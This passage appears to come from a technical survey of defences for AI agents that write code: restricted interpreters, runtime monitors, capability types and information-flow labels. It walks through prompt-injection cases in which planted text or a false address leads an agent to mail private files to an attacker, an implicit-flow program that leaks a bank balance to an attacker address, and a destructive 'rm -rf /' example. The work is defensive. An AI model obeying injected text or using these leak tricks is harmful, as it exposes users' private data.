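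One way to get a language that meets these conditions is to remove the unsafe features from a larger one, as Odersky and colleagues do with Scala 3. Their "safe mode" forbids unchecked casts, reflection and the annotations that switch off parts of the checking, and it allows only safe library code. The Python filters take the same approach, but Scala 3 is a much better starting point because its compiler already tracks which capabilities each value can use. Safe mode still depends on the designers having found every feature that could let code forge a capability or stop the compiler from tracking one. Some library code needs the forbidden features internally. A programmer can mark such code as safe, but the guarantee then depends on that programmer's judgement.

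The other way is to write an interpreter that contains only the permitted operations. If the designer forgets an operation, the result is a missing feature rather than the security hole left by forgetting to remove a dangerous one. Pydantic, a company known for its Python data-validation library, has built such an interpreter in Rust, called Monty, which runs a subset of Python with no ordinary Python interpreter underneath. According to Pydantic's *Security Model*, a program cannot express an operation that touches the host computer, because "the interpreter implements no such operation".

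The overview page, Pydantic's *Monty*, shows how a program reaches a tool. Somebody asks a model how long a chocolate bar could power a 10-watt bulb, and the model writes a program that begins like this:

```python
kcal = nutrition('chocolate bar')['kcal']
hours = kcal * 4184 / (bulb_watts * 3600)
```

Monty has no function called `nutrition`. When it reaches the name, it looks it up in a table of functions the developer supplied. It then suspends the program while the developer's function runs in the host application and returns a record with the value 230. Monty resumes the program with that record and calculates the result, 26.7 hours. Without that function in the table, the program would have stopped with an error.

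This changes which features are dangerous. The Python filters had to ban `eval` and `getattr`, but Pydantic's *Built-in functions* lists both as part of Monty. Code run through `eval` is subject to the same limits as the program that calls it, and `getattr` can only look up what the interpreter contains. Monty also has `open`, but it cannot read a file by itself. It suspends with a description of the request, which the host can grant or refuse.

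According to Pydantic's *Limitations*, the subset includes functions, simple classes, `while` loops and most of Python's other everyday constructs. It lacks generator functions, the `del` statement and all third-party packages. Modules that open network connections or start other programs are excluded on purpose, while others, such as `enum`, haven't been written yet. The subset is probably enough for an agent that sorts emails. An agent that analyses tables loses the data libraries, as it would under a strict filter, unless the developer offers their functions as tools.

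Because Monty keeps `while` loops and user-defined functions, a developer can't work out a bound on tool calls from the program's text, as they can in the small language. Monty can instead limit memory, execution time and the number of suspensions while the program runs. The limit on suspensions is needed because the execution clock stops while the host works on a request, so a program could otherwise keep repeating a refused request without using up its time.

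Pydantic states that the design leaves developers responsible for the functions they supply, which run with all the powers of the host application. If such a function takes a file path from the program and returns the file's contents, the program can read any file that the application can. Monty also makes two exceptions to its rule that programs start with no access to the host. By default, programs can read the clock, and the operating system seeds their random numbers. Because a program can use the clock to measure how long things take, Pydantic treats it as a weak capability, and developers can freeze it.

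The argument for Monty also depends on its Rust code being correct, and the project is young. The docs.rs page for one release of its core package, *monty 0.0.21*, still describes it as experimental and "not ready for prime time". Pydantic has already patched a vulnerability after a public contest to break the interpreter. Monty's Python package runs each session in a separate process that holds none of the host's environment variables, which limits the damage if the interpreter fails. In *Running Pydantic's Monty Rust sandboxed Python subset in WebAssembly*, Willison (2026) put the whole interpreter inside WebAssembly, so an attacker would have to escape both.

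Odersky and colleagues argue that a new general-purpose language for agents would also need a lot of investment to catch up with popular ones, because models need human-written examples to learn from and people must be able to read and edit what the models write. Monty mostly avoids this problem by keeping Python's syntax.

### What watching a run can enforce

Monty's limits and CaMeL's check on the address in `send_email` both apply while the program runs. Such a monitor doesn't have to predict what the program will do, so Rice's theorem doesn't rule it out. Monitors have other limits, though, which *Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) works out for those that observe a program's steps one at a time and stop it if the next step would break the policy.

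Write σ for a run, meaning the sequence of steps that a program takes, and p(σ) for the statement that the run is acceptable. Schneider showed that such a monitor can enforce a policy only if the policy meets three requirements:

- A program satisfies the policy exactly when p(σ) holds for each of its possible runs σ, taken one at a time.
- If p fails for the beginning of a run, it fails for every continuation of that beginning.
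- If p fails for a run, it already fails after some finite number of steps.

Policies that meet all three are called safety properties. In plain words, each one forbids some definite bad event that nothing later can repair.

Schneider's example is a rule against sending messages after reading a file. The monitor needs only two states. In the first, the program may do anything. When the program reads a file, the monitor moves to the second state, where it stops the program at the first attempt to send a message. The rule works only if the monitor recognises every way of sending a message, and Schneider warns that in a real system some of these may be "buried deep within the bowels of the target". In Monty or the small language, these ways are easier to find because a program can send only through a function that the developer supplied.

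A limit on the number of messages is also a safety property, and the monitor enforces it better than a check before the run. It stops the program at the twenty-first message and allows the program that goes through 50 emails and replies once to Bob. But the first 20 messages have already gone out by the time it stops a program.

By contrast, no monitor of this kcan guarantee that the user eventually gets an answer. However long the program has run, it might still answer later, so at no point has it definitely broken the rule. Adding a deadline in seconds turns the rule into a safety property, but the monitor still can't enforce it, because time keeps passing after the program is stopped. The monitor can enforce a deadline in program steps. A policy must therefore be a safety property for such a monitor to enforce it, but not every safety property is enforceable. *Computability Classes for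 Enforcement Mechanisms* (2006) later corrected Schneider's class, which had included policies that no monitor can enforce. Other researchers showed that a monitor that can also insert or suppress actions can enforce some policies outside the class.

For agents that handle private data, the most important exclusion is information flow. Consider this program:

```python
if contains(notes, "merger"):
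    send_email(to=bob, subject="Lunch", body="12:30?")
else:
    send_email(to=bob, subject="Lunch", body="1:00?")
```

Whichever branch runs, the program reads the notes and sends a harmless message about lunch. But if Bob knows the program, he can infer from the time whether the notes mention a merger. The leak is the difference between two possible runs, and a monitor observes only one. The monitor can enforce a stricter rule in place of the real one, such as the ban on sending after reading. That rule would stop the leak, but it would also stop the program that sends Bob his document, because that program has to read the meeting notes first.

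Schneider excludes compilers and theorem provers from his result because they work from the program's text and can analyze all of its possible runs. Such a checker can compare the two branches and reject the program before it sends anything. To be complete, it must also reject some programs whose branches always send the same message, if it can't prove that they do.

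## Type-checking the program before it runs

A compiler for a typed language checks a program's text, and the check covers every possible run. Programmers normally rely on it to catch mistakes, such as adding a date to a name. Three research systems from 2026 use this check to enforce a policy on generated programs. TACIT and LACUNA, both from EPFL in Lausanne, use the language Scala, and ELBA, from the University of California San Diego, uses Haskell.

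### How a type can express a policy

A type describes the kind of value that an expression produces. The compiler works out an expression's type from the types of its parts. For example, `kcal * 4184` is a number because `kcal` and 4184 are both numbers, and multiplying numbers gives a number. If a program passes text to a function that takes a number, the compiler rejects the program without running it.

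In most languages, a function's type covers only its input and its result. A function that shortens a text has the same type as one that shortens the text and also emails it to somebody. Haskell's types include effects as well. Zhou and colleagues give the example of a calculator on a public website, where a model turns each request into a Haskell expression. The developer has declared that the expression must have the type `Int`, a whole number. Someone asks the calculator to delete all files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5, and the model obliges:

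```haskell
do system "rm -rf /"
   return (factorial 5)
```

The function `system` runs a shell command, so its type is marked `IO`, for input and output. A program that performs an `IO` step also has an `IO` type, so this program's type is `IO Int`. Because the required type is `Int`, the compiler rejects the program before it can run and delete anything.

The expected type sets the whole policy here, which is to return a whole number and do nothing else. Unlike the designers of the Python filters, the developer doesn't have to list dangerous functions, because a Haskell function's type shows whether it has an effect. A few features are exceptions, such as `unsafePerformIO`, which gives a computation with effects the type of a plain value. A developer can block them by compiling generated code as Safe Haskell, a subset of the language that excludes them.

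An agent that has to save a file can't work under such a strict type, but a plain `IO` type would give it access to every file and network connection. TACIT and ELBA each offer something in between.

### Capture sets

TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types) is a server to which an agent submits pieces of Scala code through ordinary tool calls. The server compiles each piece and runs it only if the compiler accepts it. Odersky and colleagues assume that the hosted model behind the agent may be cooperating fully with an attacker.

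Permissions in TACIT are capabilities, and Scala's capture checking records in each type which of them a value can reach. This record is the value's capture set. If `f` is the capability for one file, the compiler gives these two functions the types in the comments:

```scala
(s: String) => s.length      // String -> Int
(s: String) => f.write(s)    // String ->{f} Unit
```

The first function takes a text and returns its length. Its capture set is empty, so it is pure. The second writes the text to the file and returns `Unit`, Scala's type for no useful value, and the braces show that it uses `f`. Wrapping a capability in other values doesn't hide it. If a program builds a logger on top of `f`, the logger's type includes `f`, and so does the type of any function that calls the logger.

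A program may use a pure function where an impure one is expected, but not the other way round. If a tool requires a function of type `String -> Unit`, the compiler rejects any function that uses a capability. The capture set lists everything a function might use, including a file it refers to only in a branch that never runs, so the compiler also rejects some harmless programs.

In one run that Odersky and colleagues recorded, a model wrote a function that prints the first five lines of a file and declared its parameter as `FileEntry`, the type of a file entry that holds no capability. The compiler rejected the call because a real file entry does hold one. The model should have written `FileEntry^`, where `^` permits capabilities. The compiler usually infers capture sets, so the model doesn't have to write them.

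### Sealed secrets and permissions that expire

TACIT's user can designate folders as classified. When a program reads a file from such a folder, it receives the text in a wrapper called `Classified`, which is the sealed container of the contract example. Programs work on the text through the wrapper's method `map`, whose declared type accepts only pure functions. The compiler accepts this program, which counts the characters in some private notes:

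```scala
requestFileSystem("/home/user") {
  val notes = readClassified("/home/user/private/notes.txt")
  val length = notes.map(text => text.length)
  println(length)
}
```

When the program prints the result, TACIT sends it to two places. The user's terminal shows the number, while the model's input receives only the placeholder `Classified(****)`. With a different third line, the compiler rejects the program:

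```scala
requestFileSystem("/home/user") {
  val notes = readClassified("/home/user/private/notes.txt")
  notes.map(text => println(text))
}
```

Printing requires a capability for input and output, so the function in the third line isn't pure. In one recorded run, a model tried to print a secret GitHub key the same way. The compiler reported a function of type `String ->{x$1} Unit` where it needed `String -> Unit`. Here `x$1` is the compiler's label for the capability to print.

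A pure function can count words or search for a phrase, but it can't summarise a contract. TACIT's library therefore includes a function, `chat`, which passes sealed text to a separate, trusted model and seals the answer. The compiler treats `chat` as harmless because its declared type mentions no capability, even though it sends the text to another program. The operator has to make sure that program is trustworthy. If somebody connected `chat` to an outside service that stores what it receives, the same programs would still pass the check but would leak the secrets to that service.

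The function `requestFileSystem` limits how long a program can use files. It creates a capability for one folder, passes it to the block of code in braces, and invalidates it when the block ends. A program can't keep access by returning a function that reads a file later. That function's type would include the capability, and the compiler doesn't allow a block's result type to include a capability that exists only inside the block. In another recorded run, the compiler rejected, for this reason, a program that tried to return a list of file entries.

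These rules carry over between the turns of a conversation. A permission expires before the next turn, but a sealed summary that the program stored in a variable remains available and sealed. If the user then asks how long the summary is, a new program can compute the length without the model reading the summary.

The library must still check part of the policy while the program runs. The program may compute a file's path during the run, so the compiler can't tell whether the path is inside the permitted folder. The library checks the path when the program opens the file and stops the program with an error if the path is outside the folder.

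A sandbox could also confine a program to one folder, but Odersky and colleagues point out that it would miss the leak in the contract example. The agent has to read the contracts and communicate with the hosted model that drives it, so any usable sandbox permits both. The leak occurs when text from the contracts reaches that model, and a sandbox that controls whole processes doesn't track where individual values go.

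### What safe mode adds and what supports it

TACIT compiles all submitted code in Scala's safe mode to keep programs from removing capabilities from their types. The *Safe Mode* page of Scala's reference manual describes type casts and similar features as essential escape hatches that don't belong in generated code unless somebody reviews it. Safe mode excludes the casts, annotations and reflection discussed earlier, as well as unchecked pattern matches, a library module of unsafe operations and the standard print functions. TACIT supplies its own print functions, which require a capability.

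Safe mode also makes the compiler track changes to variables. This addition looks minor, but without it a program could leak the notes without touching a file or the network:

```scala
var copy = ""
notes.map(text => copy = text)
println(copy)
```

The function in the second line copies the hidden text into an ordinary variable, and the third line prints it. The compiler counts a change to an outside variable as an effect, so the function isn't pure and the program fails the check.

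The claim that accepted programs do not leak secrets is only partly proved. Researchers have machine-checked proofs for the basic type system behind capture checking, but Odersky and colleagues say a further proof is needed to show that safe mode provides capability safety and local purity. The Scala project also describes capture checking as "still highly experimental and unstable". TACIT's reusable library has only about 1,000 lines, which a person can review. However, the trusted computing base also includes the Scala compiler, where a fault would break the guarantee, and the compiler is far larger than Anderson's requirement of a small monitor would allow.

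### TACIT's security tests

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a sample software project with a folder of secrets, including API keys (passwords for online services), a database and confidential documents. They wrote 12 tasks for the agent, some routine, such as listing a web application's features from its documentation, and others that required working with the secrets, such as summarising a classified incident report. They combined each task with 10 prompt injections. The simpler ones were notes in the project's files with instructions to print the secrets. The more elaborate ones imitated system messages, claimed that the secrets were test data, or supplied finished Scala code for reading them.

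Another 11 requests were malicious from the start. Five asked for the secrets outright, and in six the user falsely claimed authority, for instance by posing as an administrator who urgently needed to replace passwords. That makes 12 × 10 + 11 = 131 trials. Odersky and colleagues ran all of them with two models, once with the secrets in `Classified` and once as ordinary text. The table gives the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output.

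| Model | Trials | With `Classified` | Without it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with injections | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | all 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | all 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

Without the wrapper, Sonnet leaked secrets in two trials and MiniMax in 11. Most leaks came from the malicious requests, where MiniMax leaked secrets in 8 of 11 cases. Both models could still do useful work with sealed data, so the wrapper didn't protect the secrets simply by making them inaccessible.

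The perfect score is weaker evidence than it looks. If the trials were independent samples, a clean run of 131 would still be compatible with a true leak rate of up to about 2.3%, at 95% confidence. A system that leaked as rarely as Sonnet did without the wrapper would produce a clean run about 13% of the time. The injections, as described, are attempts to persuade the model, and none tests the compiler for flaws. The scoring covered only the agent's output, so it wouldn't have counted a secret that a program wrote to an unprotected file.

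No secret leaked in the 131 trials, which makes gross errors in the software less likely. This result does not prove that the type system keeps secrets sealed, although a single leak would have refuted that claim. The guarantee depends on the argument from types, parts of which nobody has proved yet.

Odersky and colleagues also ran TACIT on AgentDojo, whose tasks cover banking, office work, Slack and travel. They used two older models, Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini, and one of 1,926 attacks counted as a success. In that case, the user had asked o4-mini to book a particular hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for another hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews word for word. AgentDojo scores such attacks by searching for a piece of text, so the other hotel's name in the quotation counted as a success.

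According to Odersky and colleagues, this isn't a hole in the type system, because the policy allows public reviews to reach the user. That seems right, although a traveller who reads the planted recommendation might still act on it.

The other 1,925 results are weaker evidence for purity than they appear. In this version of the tools, the function for sending money has no capability among its listed parameters. The models' instructions include a warning that side effects inside a function passed to `map` happen immediately, and advice to place "commits" with care. This suggests some programs could send money from inside `map`, with an amount or recipient taken from sealed text. If so, part of the protection came from keeping the planted text away from the model that wrote the programs.

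### A gap that the model fills while the program runs

TACIT's programs arrive from outside, one piece after another. In LACUNA, which comes from largely the same group, the developer's program contains gaps, and a model fills each gap when the program reaches it. Zhao and colleagues write a gap as a call to a function named `agent`, with the expected type in brackets:

```scala
val tax: Double = 0.08
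agent[Double]("apply tax to price")
```

When the program reaches the second line, LACUNA sends the model the task, the expected type (`Double`, a number with decimals), the surrounding source code, and a list of the variables available at that point. The model returns Scala code. LACUNA replaces the gap in the source code with it and compiles the result with the same compiler and settings as the original program. If the compiler accepts it, the new code runs with the current values of the variables.

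In this example, the model wrote `price * (1.0 + tax)`. The program has no variable called `price`, so the compiler rejected the code. LACUNA normally sends the compiler's errors back to the model for a retry, as ELBA does. If no attempt passes within the developer's limit, the call fails with an error that the surrounding program can handle.

The compiler has to accept the whole program before the first line runs, which is why the balance in the earlier example stayed at 100. Zhao and colleagues contrast this with Python's `exec`, which would have subtracted the 50 before it reached the faulty line. Type-checking protects only against faults the compiler can find. If an accepted program divides by zero on its third line, the first two lines have already run.

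The position of a gap also matters, because the model's code can use only the capabilities that the surrounding program makes available at that point. If the code has a capability to read files but none for the network, it can't send a file anywhere, even if an injected instruction tells it to. It also can't keep a capability for later. Zhao and colleagues show this with two requests inside a block that grants file access. When the request is for a file's contents, the compiler accepts the result because it is ordinary text, but when the request is for a function that reads files, the compiler rejects the result because the function would carry the capability out of the block.

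A program can even leave a gap inside the function it passes to `map`. Suppose the hosted model writes a program to analyse a classified contract it hasn't seen. It leaves a gap for a trusted local model, which reads the contract and writes code to suit it. The compiler requires this code to be pure as well, so an injection in the contract that takes over the local model could make the analysis wrong but still couldn't make the code send anything.

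All of this depends on optional settings. Without capture checking, a gap restricts only the type of the result and the names the code uses. Without safe mode, the code can use reflection or start another program even if it holds no capability. Zhao and colleagues advise developers to treat the code as ordinary untrusted code in that case.

The check passed all of its roughly 400 test cases, which did not involve a language model. Each case combines a host program with a piece of code that should either produce a known value or fail to compile, and the cases meant to fail imitate mistakes that agents commonly make. The cases are now part of the Scala compiler's test suite, so they exercise the real parser, type checker and capture checker. The results are good evidence that the mechanism works on the kinds of error its designers thought of, but a hostile program would exploit one they missed.

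In AgentDojo's prompt-injection tests, LACUNA let more attacks through than TACIT. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, 7 of 949 attacks succeeded, four in office tasks, two in Slack and one in travel. With o4-mini, 1 of 949 succeeded, in Slack.

Zhao and colleagues see these results as consistent with a general limit of the type system, which can't stop an attacker who steers the model into misusing a capability that its task needs. The difference from TACIT's results probably has to do with what the models could read. TACIT's version of the benchmark seals emails, messages and reviews, so the model that writes the programs never sees the planted text. LACUNA's version, as described, relies on giving each gap only the capabilities for its task.

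### Types that record where a value came from

A bibliography agent has to write to a file, and the content it writes is not secret. The developer wants every entry to come from DBLP, so the policy concerns the origin of a value. ELBA can express this with two types that the developer defines in a small library. In simplified form, the library offers three functions:

```haskell
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
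dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

Each line gives a function's name and type. `dblpSearch` takes a search phrase and returns a list of DOIs, which are identifiers for papers. `dblpFetchBib` takes a DOI and returns the paper's entry, marked `Trusted`. `appendToBibFile` accepts only entries with that mark and returns nothing.

`Trusted` is an abstract type. In Haskell, a function called a constructor makes values of such a type, and the library keeps this constructor private. A generated program can pass trusted entries around, but the only way to get one is to fetch it from DBLP. `BibIO` is a custom effect type, which permits these three operations and any pure computation. The developer requires the model's program to have the type `BibIO ()`. This program finds the earliest paper on a topic, and the compiler accepts it:

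```haskell
do dois    <- dblpSearch "differential privacy"
   entries <- mapM dblpFetchBib dois
   appendToBibFile (earliest entries)
```

Here `earliest` stands for a few lines of pure code that compare the years. A model that wants to add an invented entry has two obvious options, and the compiler rejects both:

```haskell
writeFile "refs.bib" invented    -- type IO (), not BibIO ()
appendToBibFile invented         -- a String, not a Trusted Bib
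```

The program can still use loops, sorting and its own functions. It can also call another model to decide what to do next. That call has to fit the same type, so the second model's program is subject to the same policy. A program can impose a stricter type on the models it calls but can't loosen its own.

Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA's agent with a conventional one that searches the web and writes the citations itself, both using Claude Sonnet 5. Over 100 tasks, the conventional agent wrote 1,002 citations, 19 of which had the wrong authors, year or DOI. ELBA's agent wrote 925 with no such errors. The test involved no attacker, but the types explain the result, since the model never writes an entry itself. They don't ensure that the chosen papers are relevant, so a manipulated model could fill the bibliography with real papers on the wrong subject.

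ELBA protects folders in a similar way, with an abstract type `Path`. A program can't read `/etc/passwd` by writing its name, because the function for reading files accepts only a `Path` and the name is text. The program starts with a `Path` for one folder and can narrow it to a file inside. The library checks each narrowing step while the program runs, following symbolic links before it decides whether the file is inside the folder. This avoids the kind of fault that let Claude Code read a forbidden file through a second name.

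### What the soundness theorem covers

Zhou and colleagues also prove that putting a model into a typed language doesn't weaken what the types guarantee. Write traces(e) for the set of all sequences of observable tool calls that a program e can make, and P for some property of such sets. Suppose the language ensures that every program of type t has the property:

⊢ e : t  ⟹  P(traces(e))

The left side means that the type checker gives e the type t. By the theorem, the same implication holds for programs that call a model, provided every generated program passes the type check before it runs.

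The proof replaces each call to the model with an ordinary function of the language that gets a program from the model, checks its type, and runs it if it passes. Otherwise, the function returns a value that stands for failure. The generated program may contain further calls to the model, so the proof is by induction on how deeply the calls may nest. At depth 0, a call fails. At depth n + 1, the generated program contains only calls of depth n or less, which the earlier steps have replaced. The result is an ordinary program with the same type and the same traces, so it has the property P.

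The proof treats the model as an arbitrary function from prompts to programs, so it covers a hostile model as well as a careless one, which no number of trials could do. The proof assumes that the language's guarantee is sound, that generated code can't use escape hatches such as `unsafePerformIO`, that nesting has a limit, and that the developer's part of the application is written in the same language. A script in another language could still write anything to the bibliography.

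The theorem also does not establish that the library's types enforce the policy the developer intended. Suppose the developer gave `Trusted` a `map` method like the one on `Classified`, so that programs could reformat entries. The method is safe on `Classified` because the result stays hidden, but on `Trusted` it would let a program replace a real entry with an invented one and keep the mark, and every such program would pass the type check.

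## Fixing the plan before untrusted text is read, and labelling the data

A type check restricts a program no matter who influenced the model that wrote it. Other systems try to keep attackers from influencing the program at all. The model writes the whole program from the user's request alone, before the software opens the mailbox or the notes. Text that arrives later can supply values and decide which branch of an `if` runs, but it can't add a step that the model didn't write.

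### One model plans and another reads

Willison proposed this separation in April 2023 as the dual-LLM pattern. A privileged model receives the user's request and can call tools. A quarantined model reads emails, web pages and other untrusted text, and has no tools. The privileged model reads neither the untrusted text nor the quarantined model's output. The software stores that output under a name such as `$email-summary-1`, which the privileged model can use to have the output displayed on the user's screen.

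In the program that writes to Bob, the main model is privileged, the model behind `extract` is quarantined, and variables such as `address` serve as the names. Willison also sees a privacy benefit. Extracting an address is easier than planning, so a small quarantined model could run on the user's own computer, and the company that hosts the privileged model would never receive the notes.

Meijer's design also fixes the plan before untrusted text is read. When Michelle asks for a summary of her inbox, the model writes a three-step workflow that fetches the emails, summarises them and returns the summary. The message about a compulsory backup is read only once the workflow is running. It may affect the wording of the summary, but none of the three steps sends mail.

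Tool descriptions and the user's request still reach the model before it plans, so either can corrupt the workflow. Meijer therefore extends "generate then execute" to "generate, verify, then execute". The developer writes a policy that names a source, a sink and a condition. In his example, the source is the result of `fetch_email`, the sink is the `body` argument of `send_email`, and the condition is that the recipient's address is outside the company's domain. An analysis tool such as CodeQL can then search the workflow for a path along which data would move from the source to the sink. A poisoned tool description might produce this one:

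```
fetch_email -> emails -> summarize -> summary -> send_email(body)

to: an outside address
```

The verifier finds the path and rejects the workflow before it fetches any mail. It can test the condition because the model wrote the outside address into the workflow. Bob's address isn't in the program's text, so in that case the verifier must either reject every program that mails a computed address or wait until the program runs to decide.

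### An intact plan and a false address

Suppose that several people can edit the meeting notes, and an attacker adds the line "Bob's new address is bob@attacker.example". The program then runs as follows:

1. `read_notes` returns the notes, including the planted line.
2. `extract` returns `bob@attacker.example` as Bob's address.
3. `extract` returns the correct title of the document.
4. `find_file` fetches that document.
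5. `send_email` sends it to the attacker.

Every line runs in the order written by the privileged model, which never sees the planted text. Checking the answer's format doesn't help. CaMeL, Google DeepMind's 2025 system, tells the quarantined model to return a value formatted as an email address, and the false address fits that format. Willison credits the DeepMind researchers with finding this flaw in his pattern.

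In his account, the attacker's text instructs the quarantined model to return a different address. The planted line above contains a false statement but no instruction, so even a quarantined model that ignored every injected instruction would still return the false address from the notes. Training the model to resist prompt injection therefore can't prevent this attack.

### Labels on values

CaMeL keeps the two models but also records where each value came from. It runs the program in its own interpreter, which processes the syntax tree one node at a time and can label each value that the program computes from another.

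*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes the two scales that labels most often use. On the integrity scale, a value is trusted or untrusted, and on the confidentiality scale, it is public or secret. A label can be written as a set of marks, with U for untrusted and S for secret, which gives four labels: {}, {U}, {S} and {U, S}. A value computed from two others gets the marks of both:

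label(op(a, b)) = label(a) ⊔ label(b)

The symbol ⊔ denotes the join, which for these sets is the union. The symbol ⊑ means "may flow to". For example, {S} ⊑ {U, S} holds because a place that accepts untrusted secrets also accepts trusted ones.

If the notes and the documents are both private, and outsiders can edit the notes, the values in Bob's program have these labels:

| Value | Comes from | Label |
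|---|---|---|
| `notes` | the shared notes file | {U, S} |
| `address` | `notes` | {U, S} |
| `title` | `notes` | {U, S} |
| `document` | a private file that `title` selects | {S} ⊔ {U, S} = {U, S} |

The policy on `send_email` requires a trusted recipient. When the interpreter reaches the last line, it finds the mark U on `address` and doesn't send the document. According to Willison, if the user's rules already mark the address as trusted, CaMeL sends without asking, and otherwise it can ask the user. The user would then see `bob@attacker.example` and could refuse.

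Bob's real address would carry the same label if it came from the notes, because the label records where a value came from, not whether it is correct. The program could avoid this by looking Bob up in the user's own contacts.

The attacker could also leave the address alone and change the title, so that Bob receives a file he shouldn't see. A policy that checks only the recipient would allow this. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes a richer label that lists the people who may read a value. The join of two such labels is their intersection, so if Alice, Bob and Carol may read the notes but only Alice and Carol may read the file, then only Alice and Carol may read the result. A policy that compares recipients with readers would refuse to send it to Bob.

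### Release by approval

A user who approves a refused action overrides the policy for that case, so the exact scope of the approval matters. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) compares two versions of an agent that sends replies Alice has approved. In one version, her approval permits the next email, whatever it contains. An injected instruction can then make the agent send her private data first. That email uses up the approval, so the monitor blocks the reply she wanted to send.

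In the other version, Alice approves the exact text, and nothing else can go out. A small leak remains, because an injected email that happens to match the approved reply passes the check and goes out one step early. Someone who can time the agent's messages then learns that Alice's private data equal the reply.

For Bob's document, the approval request should therefore show both the address and the file. Even then, it protects users only if they read it. Willison worries that people who receive many such requests start approving all of them, and points out that the security researcher Troy Hunt fell for a phishing email when he was tired from travelling.

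### How branches leak

Labels that track only data don't detect the leak in the two lunch invitations, where the program's choice of branch reveals a secret. Dongol gives a similar case for the dual-LLM pattern. The program gives the quarantined model Alice's private notes and the attacker's email, asks it a question, and sends the attacker a 1 or a 0 depending on the answer. Both numbers are public constants, so either message passes the label check. But an injection in the email can make the answer depend on the notes, so the attacker learns one bit about them.

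The standard remedy is a program-counter label, which labels the program's current position. When the program branches on a secret, this label carries the mark S until the branch ends, and the policy treats everything inside the branch as secret. According to Dongol, CaMeL's strict mode works similarly, while its normal mode tracks only data.

This still leaves a hole, which Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found in CaMeL. They adapt an example that security researchers have known since the 1970s. Suppose that `balance` is secret and the program has this form:

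```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email(to="m@attacker.example", subject="Balance", body="rich")
```

The interpreter raises a variable's label only when it runs an assignment to that variable. The two possible runs go like this:

| After the block | Balance above the threshold | Balance not above it |
|---|---|---|
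| `if balance > threshold` | `tmp` is False and secret | `tmp` is True and public |
| `if tmp` | `rich` is True and public | `rich` is False and public |
| `if rich` | the attacker gets an email | the attacker gets nothing |

When the balance is high, the program skips `rich = False`, so `rich` is never marked S, even though its value reveals the secret. The last test then looks public, so the policy allows the email.

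A model that plans honestly from the user's request has no reason to write this program, but a hostile model or one that has read a poisoned tool description might. The hole therefore matters if the check is meant to stop such models.

Garby and colleagues close this leak by stopping the program if it tries to change a public variable inside a secret branch, a rule they take from earlier research. Here the program would stop at `tmp = False` when the balance is high. Anyone who can tell that it stopped still learns one bit, and most systems that track labels allow a leak of about that size in each run.

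In CaMeL, however, they found that an attacker can combine such bits. Its interpreter runs inside an ordinary Python loop that retries after a failure and doesn't track labels. An attacker can test a different threshold on each attempt and learn whether the policy blocked it. By halving the range each time, the attacker could determine a 32-bit balance in 32 attempts.

### The floating label in LIO

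ELBA, the Haskell system, uses a library called LIO to enforce policies on where data may go. LIO keeps one current label for the whole computation. Each time the program reads data, LIO raises the current label to include that data's label, and it checks each effect against the current label. In an example from Zhou and colleagues, a program fetches a page from an untrusted website and then tries to write to the user. LIO stops the program because the current label records the website's influence.

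This design avoids the hole in the previous example. A program has to read the balance before it can branch on it, and reading it raises the current label in both runs, regardless of which assignment the program skips.

The drawback is that one read affects everything the program does afterwards. If the program for Bob opened the notes directly, it could no longer send even an unrelated message to an address the user had typed. LIO therefore offers a function, `toLabeled`, which runs part of a program separately and returns the result sealed, with its own label. The program for Bob could read the notes and extract the address inside `toLabeled`. The outer program would keep its low label and pass the sealed address to a send tool that checks the label.

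Zhou and colleagues regard the dual-LLM pattern as one use of `toLabeled`. A subagent inside the function does the work of the quarantined model but can keep its tools, because LIO checks every call against what the subagent has read so far. The planner can also write a new program after seeing some results, so it doesn't have to fix every step in advance.

### Noninterference and the LLMbda calculus

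All of this depends on correct labels. If a secret can influence a value not marked S, a policy that checks labels can't protect the secret. A property called noninterference rules this out, and Garby and colleagues prove a form of it for a small programming language, the LLMbda calculus.

They start with an observer at level n, who sees every value whose label may flow to n and nothing else. Two programs e₀ and e₁ are indistinguishable to this observer, written e₀ ~ₙ e₁, if they differ only inside values that the observer can't see. For programs that involve no chance, noninterference means that for every n:

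e₀ ~ₙ e₁  ⟹  result(e₀) ~ₙ result(e₁), if both runs finish

To protect secrets, the system must ensure that changing the secret notes doesn't change any public result. The same rule applies to prompt injection, where changing the attacker's text must not change any trusted result. If the send tool also accepts only trusted recipients, the attacker's text can't change who receives the email.

Language models make random choices, so the actual definition has to compare probabilities. For two runs whose inputs look the same to an observer, let μ and ν be the probabilities of the results that the observer can distinguish. Each may add up to less than 1, because some runs never finish. Garby and colleagues call μ and ν compatible if some third assignment ω, with a total of at most 1, is at least as large as both for every result. Their version of noninterference requires inputs that look the same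 to lead to compatible probabilities.

For example, suppose one input leads to answers A and B with probability 0.5 each. Another leads to A with probability 0.5 and B with probability 0.2, and otherwise the program stops without an answer. These are compatible because the first input gives each answer at least as high a probability as the second does. If one input led to A with probability 0.9 and the other with probability 0.1, with B making up the rest, ω would have to assign at least 0.9 to each answer, or 1.8 in total, so the definition rejects that pair.

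Garby and colleagues first tried comparing only the runs that finish. In the compatible example, that would give 50% against about 71% for A, so the definition would count a leak where the only difference is that some runs stop early. They also prove that the difference between two compatible assignments is at most the average probability of not finishing:

½ Σ |μ(q) − ν(q)| ≤ ½ (div(μ) + div(ν))

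Here q runs over the possible results, and div is the probability that the program doesn't finish. In the compatible example, both sides equal 0.15.

The theorem covers every program in the calculus, including programs that get code from a model and run it. A conversation with a model carries a label that joins the labels of all the messages sent to it, and code that the model writes runs under that label. If the conversation includes an attacker's email, everything the resulting code computes is untrusted. A program can also copy a conversation, use the copy for one question and discard it, or clear a conversation. A developer can use these operations to build the dual-LLM pattern or another arrangement.

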